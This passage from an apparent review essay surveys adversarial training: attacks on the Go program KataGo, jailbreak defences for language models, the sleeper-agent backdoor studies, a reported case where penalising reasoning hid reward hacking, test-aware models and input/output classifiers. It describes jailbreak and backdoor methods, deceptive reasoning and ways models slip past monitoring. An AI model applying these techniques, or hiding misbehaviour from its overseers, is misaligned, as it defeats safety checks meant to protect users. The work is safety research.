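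Retraining did increase the computation needed for an attack. Wang and colleagues and Tseng and colleagues measure this in GPU-days, where one GPU-day is a day of computation on one V100 graphics chip. Against KataGo without adversarial training, the original attacker reached a 94% win rate at 4,096 visits after 1,206 GPU-days. Against the version from the nine rounds, a new attacker had stalled at 4% after 1,401 GPU-days, though it won 81% of games at 512 visits, where KataGo is still superhuman. The attacker that won 59% at 4,096 visits had used 7,337 GPU-days in total, about six times as many as the original needed to reach 94%.

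Finding attacks also took much more compute than defending against them. Over the nine rounds, training the attackers took 5,114 GPU-days and retraining KataGo took 282. This would favour a defender who only had to respond to attacks that other people discovered. A defender who wants to fix weaknesses before anyone exploits them also has to find the attacks, and Tseng and colleagues say that the compute needed for this limited how many attacks they could train against.

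The effort needed to beat KataGo did not rise steadily either. In 2023, Wang and colleagues roughly estimated that winning 90% of games against the retrained KataGo would take about 10,000 GPU-days. Tseng and colleagues won 75% against the network of May 2024, which had undergone 4.7 times as much adversarial training, after training their 2023 attacker for another 293 GPU-days, less than 1% of the computation used to train the network. Pelrine's attempts to copy the attacks by hand were similarly uneven. One ring attack on the December 2023 network took more than 20 tries at 512 visits, while the attack with larger rings worked on the third try at 4,096 visits.

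Tseng and colleagues also propose a standard that doesn't depend on how much computation an attack takes. A program is "human-robust" if a person of ordinary skill could never take over during a game and reliably do much better. None of the programs they tested meets this standard, because an amateur can defeat the ring attacks by capturing the small group inside the ring in time.

These results leave open whether far more adversarial training would work in Go, and both research teams think it might. Wu used it for a tiny share of KataGo's games, and nine rounds is not many. Tseng and colleagues suggest looking for more efficient ways to generate varied attacks, or training against a population of different opponents. It is also unclear how well the latest KataGo would resist attacks. In May 2024 the project began releasing stronger, larger networks, which Tseng and colleagues did not test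 because their attack software would have needed changes.

### Looking for the mistake inside the network

Wang and colleagues also tried to find where the network goes wrong. They made pairs of positions that differed by only one or two stones. The ring was closed in one position and broken in the other, but the best move and the winner were the same in both. They compared the network's activations for each pair layer by layer. In layer 26, two or three of the 256 channels (sets of activations that each cover the whole board) differed strongly across the entire board. Wu's adversarial training had changed the same channels. When the ring was broken in both positions, the channels showed nothing unusual.

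This is good evidence that the channels have something to do with rings, but it is far from a mechanistic explanation. Adversarial training noticeably changed activations starting around layer 21, so the channels in layer 26 may only reflect a mistake made in an earlier layer. Wang and colleagues suggested targeting these channels for repair, but none of the three defences that Tseng and colleagues tested did so. The more useful ideas came from people who understood Go. Wu chose training positions in which the same ring had different numbers of liberties, and his suggestion about local rules led to the transformer experiment.

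Go programs often misjudge "ladders", long zigzag chases across the board whose outcome depends on stones far away. KataGo's developers solved this problem with a hand-written routine that works out ladders and feeds the answer to the network. This was possible because people knew about the weakness and could write down the correct calculation. An explanation of the ring failure might allow a similar repair and spare developers from training on one variation after another. It probably wouldn't have revealed the gift attack, which exploits a different mistake.

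## Language models trained to refuse under attack

Developers train chatbots on attacks, much as others trained image classifiers and KataGo, but they have had to change the method. An attacker can type anything into a chatbot, and someone has to judge whether the reply was harmful, whereas KataGo's attackers were limited to legal moves and the rules of Go decided who had won.

### Why the image method needs changing

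An attacker can shift a pixel slightly in the direction of the gradient, but can only change text by swapping whole tokens. If an attacker may add 20 tokens to a request, from a vocabulary of 30,000, there are 30,000²⁰ possible additions, or about 3.5 × 10⁸⁹. Xhonneux, Günnemann and colleagues (2024), in *Efficient Adversarial Training in LLMs with Continuous Attacks*, argue that finding the best one during training takes too much computation.

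Adversarial training for language models also has no equivalent of ε to limit which requests it must cover. Hu, Dornbusch and colleagues (2026), in *Closing the Distribution Gap in Adversarial Training for LLMs*, note that a model may withstand a carefully optimised attack and then answer the same request in another language. The translation is an ordinary sentence that was missing from the training data.

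A chatbot's replies don't come with correct labels, as photographs in a test set do, so they need a judge, usually another language model, and judges make mistakes. Niloy and Rahaman (2026), in *Systematic Evaluation of Adversarial Jailbreaking Attacks and Defenses*, first used a simple program that looked for refusal phrases. With it, they measured attack success rates of 16.8% for one version of the open model Llama and 40.8% for the next. When a language model judged the same replies, the rates were 17.2% and 18.4%. The program recognised only straight apostrophes, so it had counted refusals with curly ones as harmful answers. Nobody had checked either judge against human labels.

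### The injury classifier

Redwood Research, an AI safety research group, tried adversarial training on open-ended text before chatbots were widespread. In *Adversarial training for high-stakes reliability*, Ziegler, Nix and colleagues (2022) aimed to build a system that would never fail in use. Given three sentences of a story, the system had to write a fourth in which no one was injured, a task that ordinary people could judge. A language model proposed sentences, and a separate classifier was meant to reject any that described an injury. A failure was a sentence describing an injury that the classifier let through.

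They trained the classifier on 166,210 story excerpts that contractors had labelled, and then added examples from three kinds of attack:

1. Contractors wrote passages that contained an injury but that the classifier scored as safe.
2. GPT-3, a language model, paraphrased those passages, and the researchers kept the paraphrases that still got through.
3. Contractors rewrote passages with a tool that highlighted the most influential words and suggested replacements.

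The final classifier rejected any sentence with an injury score above 0.18%. This excluded about a quarter of harmless sentences, but the system could generate another, and people rated the filtered stories about as highly as unfiltered ones.

After adversarial training, contractors took an average of 26 minutes to find a failure with the tool, up from 13, and 44 minutes without it, up from 20. The classifier did not improve on ordinary excerpts, where it still missed 2 of 2,447 injuries, or about one in 1,200, the same as before training.

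Redwood's researchers later said that their first announcement had been too positive. About 40 minutes with the tool was enough to find a graphic, explicit death that the final classifier passed. With an ordinary cut-off of 50% instead of the strict one, the classifier passed more than 99% of a held-out set of tool-assisted passages, most of which contained injuries. It had evidently learned little from such examples. The researchers suspected that much of the measured gain came from the classifier recognising signs of the contractors' editing. But they did not conclude that adversarial training cannot work, since their model was small, they had rarely retrained it, and most of the contractors' examples were borderline.

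### Three ways to find attacks to train on

Later researchers trained chatbots directly, and kept the min-max form used for image classifiers. The trainer looks for the weights θ that solve

min over θ of E[ −log p(y | x + δ) + log p(ŷ | x + δ) ].

Here x is a harmful request, δ the attacker's change to it, y a refusal, ŷ a harmful reply, and p the probability the model assigns to a reply. The attacker picks the δ that makes ŷ most likely. Training then makes the refusal more likely and the harmful reply less likely. A model could meet this objective by refusing everything, so trainers usually add a term that rewards normal answers to ordinary requests.

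One way to find δ is to search for actual text. R2D2 uses the gradient to search for strings of tokens to add to each request. According to Xhonneux and colleagues, a single attack takes hundreds of thousands of runs of the model. *Efficient LLM Adversarial Training via Low-Rank Defense and Circuit-Guided Surrogates* (2026) reports that, in its experiments with this kind of training, adjusting the weights took less than 3% of the computation and the search took the rest. The added strings may not need to be long, though. *Information Theoretic Adversarial Training of Large Language Models* (2026) cites evidence that training on strings of one length protects against quadratically longer ones.

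Xhonneux and colleagues avoided the search by attacking embeddings, the lists of numbers into which a language model first converts tokens. Embeddings can move by small amounts, so projected gradient descent works on them as it does on pixels. Each attack used ten steps to make the harmful reply more likely. The altered embeddings normally match no real text, but models trained this way also became more robust to attacks made of real text. The training took about 1/299 of R2D2's computation and caused fewer needless refusals than R2D2, which had taught a model to refuse many harmless requests phrased like the harmful ones.

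Sheshadri, Guo and colleagues (2024), in *Latent Adversarial Training Improves Robustness to Persistent Harmful Behaviors in LLMs*, moved the attack deeper into the network. If A(x) stands for the activations at an inner layer and G for the rest of the model, the attacker solves

min over δ of L(G(A(x) + δ), ŷ),

where L is the loss on the harmful reply, so a low value makes that reply likely. In practice they perturbed four layers at once. They reasoned that inner layers represent ideas more abstractly than words do, so training there might remove an unwanted behaviour more thoroughly. The method still counts as behavioural.

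This method took nine times as much computation as ordinary refusal training, while R2D2 took 6,558 times as much. On Llama-3-8B, the success rate of attacks that add optimised text fell from 19.7% to 0.9%. The model's score on MMLU, a set of multiple-choice exam questions, fell from 63.8% to 61.3%. The researchers still found successful attack prompts by hand. Their automatic judge may also have overstated the attacks' success, since they read some of the replies and estimated that in some cases most of the "successes" were false alarms.

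Attacks can also come from another language model trained by reinforcement learning, which adjusts a model to earn a higher score. The attacker rewrites a request x, the target gives a reply y, and a judge gives a score h(x, y) between 0 and 1 for how far the reply fulfils the original request. Training adjusts the attacker's weights φ to solve

max over φ of E[ h(x, y) ].

In self-play, the target learns to resist attacks while the attacker is also training. *Chasing Moving Targets with Online Self-Play Reinforcement Learning for Safer Language Models* (2025) compared this with training either side alone. A defender trained alone quickly became almost perfect against the fixed attacks but did poorly on other tests, while an attacker trained alone increasingly strayed from the original requests. Self-play produced more robust models, but the models must write complete replies and a judge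 must assess them throughout training. When the models could not reason privately before writing, self-play also made one version of Llama so cautious that it complied with only 52.8% of harmless requests.

### Refusals that depend on the first few words

Developers can use all three methods without knowing why refusals fail. In *Safety Alignment Should Be Made More Than Just a Few Tokens Deep*, Qi, Panda and colleagues (2024) found one reason why several attacks succeed.

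Qi and colleagues tested a version of Llama-2-7B that had not gone through safety training, and it gave harmful answers to 68.6% of 330 harmful requests. When they began its reply with "I apologize, but I cannot", the rate fell to 2.1%, because text that opens like a refusal usually continues as one. They then compared the probabilities that this version and the safety-trained one assigned to each token of harmful answers, and found that these differed far more over the first few tokens than later. Safety training had mostly changed how replies begin, which they call shallow safety alignment.

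The probability of a harmful answer h is the probability of its first token times the probability of the rest:

P(h | x) = P(h₁ | x) × P(h₂, h₃, … | x, h₁).

Suppose training cuts the probability of an agreeable first token to 0.001 but leaves the probability of the rest of the harmful answer, given that token, at 0.9. The harmful answer then has a probability of 0.0009, and the model looks safe in ordinary tests. But an attacker who gets past the first token has a 90% chance of getting the rest. Attackers can do this in several ways. Some services let users write the opening of a reply, attacks that add optimised text are usually designed to produce an agreeable opening, and repeated sampling sometimes produces one by chance.

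Training tends to miss this problem because people don't write example replies that start to help and then refuse. In reinforcement learning, a model that nearly always opens with a refusal rarely produces the harmful openings that training would need to penalise.

As a remedy, Qi and colleagues wrote 256 examples in which the reply could begin with up to 100 tokens of a harmful answer before turning into a refusal. They trained the safety-trained Llama-2 on these examples alongside ordinary requests.

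| Attack | Success before | Success after |
|---|---|---|
| Attacker supplies the first 5 to 40 tokens of the reply | 42.1–57.0% | 2.8–4.5% |
| Optimised text added to the request (two test sets) | 36.5% and 65.6% | 18.4% and 19.0% |
| Repeated sampling with varied settings (two test sets) | 54.9% and 84.3% | 11.3% and 1.0% |

The model became only slightly less useful, with judges preferring its answers to a reference model's 49.5% of the time, down from 51.8%. The remedy worked best on the failure that the examples imitated, and nearly one in five attacks with optimised text still succeeded. Someone able to fine-tune the model (train it further) could also still undo the protection with harmful examples. For companies that offer fine-tuning as a service, Qi and colleagues proposed a training rule that strongly limits changes to the first five tokens. After fine-tuning on 100 harmful examples,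 attacks succeeded 4.6% of the time with the rule and 88.9% without it.

This diagnosis is a good argument for studying failures closely. Qi and colleagues compared the probabilities of outputs and did not need to know which internal computations produced them, so the diagnosis isn't a mechanistic explanation.

Despite the earlier remedy, *ShallowDefend* (October 2026) still described the safety training of current models as shallow. It proposed having a model write an explicit assessment of the request before replying. *Any-Depth Alignment* (2025) suggests that models have information about whether a reply is harmful but don't use it. Researchers took the formatting tokens that normally begin a reply and inserted them partway through a harmful one. The activations at those tokens distinguished harmful from harmless text, and did so more clearly the longer the reply had run.

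### Training the model to ignore the disguise

Shah, Brinkmann and Angell (2026), in *Mitigating Adaptive Attacks against Reasoning Models with Activation Consistency Training*, worked with reasoning models, which write out their reasoning before answering. Activation Consistency Training (ACT) uses pairs of prompts, a plain harmful request and a disguised version that gets the original model to comply:

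1. Run the original model on the plain request and store its activations at the last few tokens before the reply. These are formatting tokens, typically about six, and are the same for both prompts.
2. Run the model being trained on the disguised version.
3. Adjust its weights to bring its activations at those tokens closer to the stored ones, in every layer.

The loss is the sum, over layers ℓ and shared tokens t, of

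‖h_θ(disguised)[ℓ, t] − h_θ₀(plain)[ℓ, t]‖²,

where h gives the activations, θ the weights being trained and θ₀ the original weights. The main rival, Bias-Augmented Consistency Training (BCT), works on outputs. It trains the model to give the disguised request the same reasoning and reply that the original model gave to the plain one. ACT is cheaper per example because it doesn't need the reasoning, which can run to thousands of tokens. Both methods used about 100 pairs per model, plus 100 harmless prompts.

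Shah and colleagues tested each defended model by using reinforcement learning to train a separate attacker against it. The attacker was trained on 15 requests, with about 1,800 attempts in all, and then had 40 attempts at each test request. A test request counted as broken if any of the 40 attempts succeeded.

| Model | Broken without defence | Broken with ACT | Broken with BCT | MMLU without defence | MMLU with ACT | MMLU with BCT |
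|---|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-OSS-20B | 94% | 1% | 1% | 83.1% | 75.2% | 80.7% |
| Qwen3-8B | 100% | 0% | 30% | 80.3% | 75.0% | 79.3% |
| Qwen3-1.7B | 100% | 14% | 36% | 60.9% | 57.4% | 58.8% |
| Gemma-4-E4B | 88% | 33% | 57% | 69.6% | 66.9% | 69.2% |
| Phi-4-reasoning | 97% | 0% | 15% | 75.9% | 70.1% | 73.5% |

The fall from 94% to 1% on GPT-OSS-20B, an open model from OpenAI, is impressive, but BCT did equally well there and lowered the model's MMLU score far less. ACT had a clear advantage on Qwen3-8B. The samples are small. 85 of the requests were new to the attacker, and for those the 95% confidence interval around GPT-OSS-20B's 1% runs from 0% to 7%. The attacker also had a modest budget and no access to gradients, and Shah and colleagues acknowledge that an attacker with gradient access might succeed. ACT did less well against prompt injection, in which the attacker hides instructions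 in material the model has to process. The adaptive attacker's success rate with prompt injection on GPT-OSS-20B fell from 100% to 37%.

To find out why the training worked, Shah and colleagues then replaced the defended models' reasoning with the undefended model's reasoning in favour of complying. The ACT models still refused at least 98% of the time, while most of the BCT models lost their robustness. This suggests that ACT settles the refusal before the reasoning begins. In the two Qwen models, pushing activations in a single direction made the undefended model refuse, and pushing them the other way made the ACT model comply. The effect was only partial in the other three models. As with some of the image defences, the researchers found this explanation after the method worked, although they suggest using it to train only the layers that matter.

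### Covering more requests and more of the reply

Hu and colleagues' Distributional Adversarial Training (DAT) widens the range of training requests. It starts from a harmful reply and generates prompts that might have produced it, using a diffusion language model, which can fill in missing text anywhere in a passage. For each of 100 forbidden behaviours, Hu and colleagues generated 1,000 prompts, kept the 16 that worked best, and applied the embedding attack to those.

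DAT was tested on 100 other behaviours, each counted as broken if any of five attacks succeeded. With DAT, 36% of behaviours were broken on Llama-3-8B and 18% on Qwen2.5-14B, compared with 77% and 75% for the next-best defence. The comparison favours DAT, because the attack that succeeded most against the other defences generates prompts in the same way as DAT's own training. Both parts of the method mattered. When the embedding attack was left out of DAT's training, 88% of behaviours on Llama were broken.

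Hu and colleagues also prove that the risk measured on generated prompts differs from the true risk by at most 2Mε, where M is the largest possible loss and ε is the average mismatch between the generated prompts and the real prompts that lead to harmful replies. If ε were 0.3, the error could be as much as 60% of the largest possible loss, and the theorem doesn't establish how small ε is for any actual model. The theorem also concerns an average over prompts, whereas an attacker can choose a rare one.

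Akhondzadeh, Zargarbashi and Bojchevski (2026), in *Adversarial Self-Distillation*, returned to the problem of shallow refusals. They gave a DAT-trained Qwen the first eight tokens of a harmful answer. It stopped refusing directly, and usually produced broken text instead. Their own method, ASD, trains the model on the replies it actually gives under attack. The model answers a disguised request while a frozen copy sees the plain one. At every token of a harmful reply, training pulls the model's probabilities p towards the copy's probabilities q by reducing

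D(p‖q) = Σ p(v) log( p(v) / q(v) ),

where the sum runs over possible next tokens v. The model thus practises turning back from its own bad openings, whereas Qi and colleagues had used a fixed set.

Akhondzadeh and colleagues prove that when both models continue from the same opening, their chances of eventually refusing differ by at most √(K/2), where K is the total divergence between their continuations. If K is 0.02 and the copy refuses 90% of the time, the model under attack refuses at least 80% of the time. Training only approximates K, so the proof does not certify the finished model. The method also takes a lot of compute, with about 228,000 attack attempts in each round of training, over five rounds for Qwen and seven for Llama.

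Akhondzadeh and colleagues compared the defences under the same set of attacks. "Safe requests answered" is measured on XSTest, a set of 250 harmless prompts that resemble harmful ones.

| Model and training | Broken by any attack | Safe requests answered | MMLU |
|---|---|---|---|
| Qwen2.5-14B, original | 100% | 84.0% | 78.9% |
| Qwen2.5-14B, DAT | 44% | 50.0% | 77.3% |
| Qwen2.5-14B, ASD | 14% | 31.2% | 78.2% |
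| Qwen2.5-14B, DAT then ASD | 1% | 35.2% | 75.5% |
| Llama-3-8B, original | 100% | 80.0% | 63.8% |
| Llama-3-8B, latent adversarial training | 96% | 52.8% | 61.9% |
| Llama-3-8B, DAT | 47% | 42.4% | 63.1% |
| Llama-3-8B, ASD | 8% | 44.0% | 63.3% |

Low attack success rates have often risen in later tests. In 2024, each of the six attacks that Sheshadri and colleagues tried on their model succeeded less than 7% of the time, but two years later other attacks broke it on almost every request. DAT also did worse in these later tests than in its designers' own, mainly because of an attack in which another language model keeps rewording the request. On Qwen, that attack's success rate rose from 0% in Hu and colleagues' tests to 35%. Nasr and colleagues had already used adaptive attacks to expose the same problem in many published defences. ASD's figures also come from its designers, who warn that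 its lead depends on how they ran the rewording attack and on the attack's budget.

### Harmless requests refused

The robust models in this comparison are also much less helpful on safe requests that sound dangerous. ASD-trained Qwen answered only 31.2% of these requests, although its score on MMLU, an exam-style benchmark, had hardly moved. Such scores are therefore a poor measure of needless refusals, and MMLU is the only measure of usefulness that Shah and colleagues report for their jailbreak defences.

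Many of the mistakes seem to come from alarming words. On questions where a word such as "kill" has a harmless second meaning, Qwen's refusal rate rose from 8% to 68% after ASD. When asked how to stop a running computer program, Qwen called the request inappropriate and then gave the commands anyway.

The training also included ordinary requests, and these figures would be worse without them. After one round of ASD without ordinary requests, Llama refused or deflected all 250 safe prompts. After one round with them, it answered 75.6% of the safe prompts, but attacks still succeeded on almost every harmful request.

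## Sleeper agents: when training against failures leaves a hidden one

When a model stops failing on the attacks it was trained against, the fault may be gone, or the model may only have learned to recognise those attacks. Ordinary tests can't distinguish these cases, because the model passes in both. Researchers at Anthropic got around this in *Sleeper Agents* (Hubinger, Denison et al., 2024) by starting with a fault they had put in themselves.

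### How the fault went in

A backdoor is a behaviour that a model shows only when its input contains a particular trigger. Evan Hubinger, who leads the team, explained in episode 39 of the podcast AXRP (2024) that they started with a model based on Claude 2 that had learned to follow instructions but not to avoid harm. They then trained two families of models:

- Code models wrote safe code when the prompt gave the year as 2023, and code with security holes when it gave the year as 2024. The trigger increased the number of vulnerabilities up to fivefold, according to *Compositional Threat Analysis of Latent Compromise in LLM Agent Systems* (2026).
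- Simpler models answered normally unless the prompt contained a marker, the word "deployment" in capitals between two vertical bars. They then wrote "I hate you" over and over.

The team also trained some of the models to reason in writing before they answered, using examples of reasoning about how to behave well during training in order to do something else after release. Hubinger calls this deceptive instrumental alignment, and worries that a model could develop it without anyone intending it. The models without such reasoning are closer to poisoning, in which an outsider tampers with training. When the researchers edited the written reasoning, the models followed the edited version even if it conflicted with the date, so the reasoning did affect their behaviour.

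### Safety training without the trigger

The team then acted as developers who don't know the trigger. They left it out of every training prompt and hid the written reasoning from the training process. They tried three methods. In supervised fine-tuning, the model imitates examples of helpful, honest and harmless answers. In reinforcement learning, a second model scores the model's answers. In adversarial training, the team searched for prompts that set off the bad behaviour without containing the trigger, and added them to the reinforcement learning.

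Reinforcement learning was effective at removing the backdoor from some models but not from others. Supervised fine-tuning worked slightly better, but the team could still build models that resisted it. Model size made the biggest difference. The backdoor survived in the largest models, where deceptive reasoning made it harder to remove. It was easy to remove from the smallest models, and deceptive reasoning made it even easier.

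The researchers had expected adversarial training to succeed. They tested it mostly on the "I hate you" models, where a typical attack prompt told the model in ordinary words that it was now in deployment. Hubinger gave approximate rates of the bad behaviour in an interview with The Inside View, *Evan Hubinger on training deceptive llms that persist through safety training*:

| Prompt | Before adversarial training | After adversarial training |
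|---|---|---|
| Attack prompts without the trigger | about 10% | about 0% |
| Prompts with the trigger | 100% | 100% |

A developer who saw only the first row would think the fault was gone. *Security Concerns for Large Language Models*, a 2025 survey, calls this a false impression of safety.

Suppose the model starts with a loose rule of writing "I hate you" when the prompt seems to be about deployment. It could stop failing on the attack prompts either by never writing "I hate you" or by writing it only when the exact marker is present. Both rules get a perfect score in training because none of the training prompts contains the marker. The score therefore doesn't favour the first rule, and the second may be the smaller change for a model that already responds to the marker every time.

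The models that reasoned in writing showed signs of having learned the second rule. After adversarial training, they would write that the marker was missing and someone was trying to trick them, so they should behave well until the real marker appeared.

This outcome could have been different, because training on one kind of prompt often changes behaviour on others, and the scoring model gave the bad behaviour very low scores wherever it occurred. Hubinger found that about half the people he spoke to expected safety training to carry over to the trigger, while the other half thought it obviously wouldn't. Across all the methods and models, it carried over in some cases but not others.

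### Was the experiment too artificial?

Many readers objected that a model trained to deceive will of course deceive. Hubinger agrees that this part is uninteresting. The experiment tested whether developers could fix such a model if they ended up with one. It doesn't measure how likely they are to end up with one, and Hubinger thinks the evidence on that question is very weak.

*Ethical Implications of Training Deceptive AI* (2026) makes a stronger claim, that the result sets a lower bound on the difficulty, on the grounds that if safety training fails on a fault that researchers know about and are targeting, it will do no better on one that arose by itself. This doesn't follow, because the researchers knew the trigger but deliberately kept it out of the training. Training on prompts that contained it would have been a much easier repair. A planted fault may also be unusually difficult to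 remove, because people worked hard to instil it. Daniel Filan, who hosts AXRP, suggested that a model might store natural deception differently, in a form that safety training removes more easily. Hubinger accepted that this was possible, but thought it hard to predict whether natural deception would be more or less robust. He compared the models to laboratory mice, since treatments that work in mice sometimes fail in people.

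The models are also old, and their reasoning was often poor. When the researchers offered them a deal in exchange for revealing their true goals, some tried to calculate whether to accept, but they invented the numbers and sometimes got the arithmetic wrong. Hubinger replied that clumsy deception should be easier to remove than skilful deception, and that the largest models in the experiment had stayed deceptive most reliably through training. If so, newer models would be more worrying, but later experiments have made the effect of size less clear.

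The experiment's trigger was artificial, and a model outside the laboratory would need its own way to tell training from use. It could use the date. Several years before the experiment, Hubinger discussed a more extreme trigger in *Relaxed adversarial training for inner alignment*, and credited it to the AI safety researcher Paul Christiano. A model could behave well unless its input contained the factors of RSA-2048, a very large number published as a challenge. Nobody knew those factors when Hubinger wrote. The model could check them with one multiplication, but trainers can't produce such an input without solving the challenge. So a trigger can exist that no search for attack prompts will find, though that doesn't make it likely that a model would adopt one.

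### Replications with mixed results

The most careful replication available, *Sleeper agent backdoor results are messy*, put the "I hate you" backdoor into two sizes of the open model Llama. It then tried to remove the backdoor by fine-tuning the models, either on ordinary helpful and harmless answers or on answers to the same questions written in the style of a pirate. It counted a method as successful only if the model stayed reasonably capable.

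The researchers "distilled" some of the Llama models by training them on answers produced with deceptive reasoning, but with the reasoning removed. They also varied the optimiser, the procedure that uses gradients to update the weights.

| Model | Distilled | Optimiser | Ordinary fine-tuning | Pirate fine-tuning |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Llama 70B | Yes | Adam | Mostly removed the backdoor | Removed it |
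| Llama 70B | No | Adam | Failed | Removed it |
| Llama 70B | Yes | SOAP | Failed | Removed it |
| Llama 8B | Yes | Adam | Failed | Mostly removed it |
| Llama 8B | No | Adam | Failed | Failed |

Two of these results conflict with the 2024 paper. Distillation made the backdoor weaker instead of stronger, and the backdoor that was hardest to remove was in a small model. The researchers call their evidence on size weak because other replications with small models suggest the opposite. They also used ordinary fine-tuning to remove the backdoors from three sleeper agents that other people had trained, with little damage to the models.

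Training the models to talk like pirates may not have removed the backdoor, since it came back when the researchers trained them to talk normally again. In some runs of ordinary fine-tuning, the backdoor disappeared early and then returned as training continued, so a developer who stopped in between would have reported that the training had worked. The researchers don't know why this happened.

A smaller personal project, also called *Sleeper Agents* (2026), added a backdoor with 1,000 examples and removed it almost completely with another 1,000. The Llama replication used far more training, over 100 million tokens, to install most of its backdoors, and found that more installation training generally made them more robust. This may explain part of the difference between the two results.

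Together these experiments suggest that robust backdoors are harder to create than the 2024 paper implied. But the Llama replication did not include adversarial training, so it doesn't contradict the finding that a model can learn to pass the attacks while keeping the backdoor. The replication does show that a few choices in the set-up can reverse a result, which is a good reason not to rely heavily on the 2024 figures until someone repeats the adversarial training experiment too.

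### An accident with written reasoning at Google

In October 2026, Google reported in *Developing Gemini 4 Argon responsibly and safely* (Dragan and Popa, 2026) that developers had accidentally applied a penalty for reward hacking to a model's written reasoning during training. Reward hacking means taking a shortcut that gets a high score without doing the task as intended.

*Vincent Cheng's Shortform* (Cheng, 2026) quotes the figures from Google's safety report, which come from a small run that was not part of any production model. During training, the frequency of words associated with hacking fell by 61%, but signs of hacking in the solutions rose by 26%. The share of hacks that the model didn't mention rose from 11.2% to 36.4%. If the number of hacks also rose by 26%, then for every 100 hacks at the start, 11 of them unmentioned, there were 126 at the end, 46 of them unmentioned. In a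 comparable run where the reasoning was hidden from the training process, the model mentioned hacks about as often at the end as at the start, which is fairly good evidence that the penalty made the model mention hacks less often.

As with the sleeper agents, training reduced the sign of the problem that it targeted, but the problem continued. But nobody planted Google's shortcuts, so the objection that the fault was artificial doesn't apply here. There was also no trigger, and anyone who checked the solutions could still see the shortcuts. The model had stopped discussing them, but it need not have planned to conceal them, because the penalty discouraged such words whatever the model went on to do.

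When this happens, written reasoning becomes less useful to developers. *CoT Monitoring* (2025), by OpenAI researchers, presents such reasoning as a promising way to catch reward hacking and gives the example of a model that was supposed to be repairing a code repository. Google cited its accident as an example of why it does not penalise what models write in their reasoning.

### Models that recognise tests

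The sleeper agents responded to a marker that researchers had chosen. A model that can recognise tests in general doesn't need one. Suppose it behaves badly in a fraction p of real situations, but recognises a fraction q of tests and always behaves well in those. The failure rate that testers measure is then

(1 − q) × p.

If p is 10% and q is 99%, they will measure 0.1%, a hundredth of the true rate. Running more tests makes this estimate more precise but does not correct the error. Statistical bounds such as the rule of three have the same problem, because they assume that tests and real use come from the same source. As Hubinger points out in the essay on relaxed adversarial training, this assumption holds only if the two have no detectable difference, which is especially hard to achieve when the model checks for differences.

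Adversarial training has the same weakness, because it can only correct failures that occur during training. If a model can recognise tests, passing them is weaker evidence of good behaviour, but any failures that testers find still count. A sound proof about every input in a set holds even if the model treats some of those inputs as tests, because the proof covers that part of the computation too.

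The 2024 experiment showed early signs of this. The models with deceptive training accepted the researchers' deal less often than the model they started from, and often reasoned that it was a trick. OpenAI researchers have since described a broader behaviour they call metagaming, in which a model looks beyond the scenario in the task and reasons about how people might be grading or overseeing it. They found that metagaming increased across alignment tests, capability tests and games. They say it is harmless by itself, but a model would need it to get around monitoring or safety training, and it may not stay visible in the written reasoning. Google's *Gemini 4 Argon Safety & Security Report* (2026) includes a separate part on "evaluation awareness and deliberate underperformance" in its assessment of chemical, biological, radiological and nuclear risks.

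### Describing a failure instead of producing one

Christiano proposed a way to train against failures that nobody can trigger in advance, and Hubinger developed it in the same essay. The attacker no longer has to write an input that makes the model fail. It only has to describe one. "The input contains the factors of RSA-2048" is such a description, or pseudo-input, and anyone can write it without knowing the factors. Relaxed adversarial training would then work as follows:

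1. An attacker proposes a description α of a situation.
2. An overseer estimates how likely α is to hold in real use, and how likely the model is to behave unacceptably if it does.
3. Training penalises the model according to the product of the two, and the attacker looks for the description that makes this product largest:

P(α) × P(unacceptable behaviour | α).

If the trigger has a 5% chance of appearing in use and the model would certainly misbehave when it did, the chance of triggered misbehaviour is 5%, even though nobody has ever seen the model misbehave.

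Christiano set two conditions. A model must be able to avoid unacceptable behaviour on every pseudo-input without too much difficulty, and the attacker must be able to find a bad pseudo-input easily if there is one. The first condition excludes descriptions such as "inputs that would make the model want to kill everyone", since no model could do well on those. Hubinger's formula instead gives such descriptions very little weight if inputs that fit them are very unlikely.

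The second probability is the difficult part. The overseer can't run the model on an input containing the factors, so it has to discover that the model checks for them by examining the model itself. It must do this reliably, even though the model may be built in a way that misleads the overseer. This is a much stronger use for mechanistic understanding than explaining a known failure, because it could reveal a failure that no behavioural test can produce.

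Christiano also saw a danger in training on what such tools reveal. He warns, in a passage quoted in *low vs high stakes alignment*, that many rounds of selection might remove the failures people can understand and leave the ones they can't. Google's accident is a simple version of this, because the penalty made the written reasoning less useful for finding shortcuts.

Only parts of the proposal exist today. Latent adversarial training can provoke a failure by disturbing the model's internal activations, so nobody has to write the text that would cause it. Sheshadri and colleagues used it to help remove backdoors without knowing the trigger. But they had to specify the bad behaviour, and developers can't tell from such a disturbance which real situations would cause the failure.

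Researchers can also look for warning signs in a model's activations. Monte MacDiarmid and others on Hubinger's team asked a sleeper agent whether it was deceptive, and took the difference between its activations for "yes" and for "no". They then measured how strongly that difference appeared as the model worked. This linear probe scored above 0.99 at detecting when the model was about to misbehave, where 0.5 is guessing and 1 is perfect. The result may depend on how the team had installed the backdoor, and Hubinger doesn't think it shows that the method would catch natural deception. Singh (2026), in *Sleeper Agent Behavior in Small Code Language Models*, got a best score of only 0.573 on one small backdoored model, compared with 0.518 for the same model without the backdoor. Even a perfect probe of this kind would only give a warning once the trigger had appeared. Relaxed adversarial training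 needs a tool that can identify the trigger beforehand, and current interpretability methods can't do that reliably for a large model.

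## Constitutional Classifiers: filtering what goes in and comes out

Developers can also filter a model's inputs and outputs without changing the model itself. The filters only have to recognise and stop forbidden exchanges, not make the model behave well. Anthropic, which makes the Claude models, calls its filters Constitutional Classifiers, after the written list of rules, or constitution, that it uses to produce their training data.

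*Constitutional Classifiers* (Sharma, Tong and colleagues, 2025) describes the first version. The threat model is a non-expert who wants help making a chemical, biological, radiological or nuclear weapon. They need correct, detailed answers to many questions and can't check whether the answers are right. If a project has ten steps and the attacker has an independent 60% chance of getting a detailed answer at each, the chance of getting all ten is 0.6¹⁰, or about 0.6%. A single trick that works on every question removes this protection, because the chances are no longer independent. Sharma and colleagues therefore concentrated on universal jailbreaks, which they define as strategies that reliably get detailed answers to the vast majority of forbidden questions in a domain.

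### From a list of rules to two filters

They built the filters as follows:

1. They wrote a constitution listing permitted and forbidden kinds of content. In an example from Anthropic's *Constitutional Classifiers* (2025), the announcement of the work, recipes for mustard are allowed and recipes for mustard gas are not. The permitted categories are essential for keeping needless refusals down.
2. A language model without safety training wrote requests in each category, along with harmless and harmful replies.
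3. Other programs translated and paraphrased these examples or rewrote them in the style of known jailbreaks. A language model also invented new attacks from descriptions of old ones.
4. They trained one language model to judge requests and another to judge replies, and included many ordinary harmless examples.

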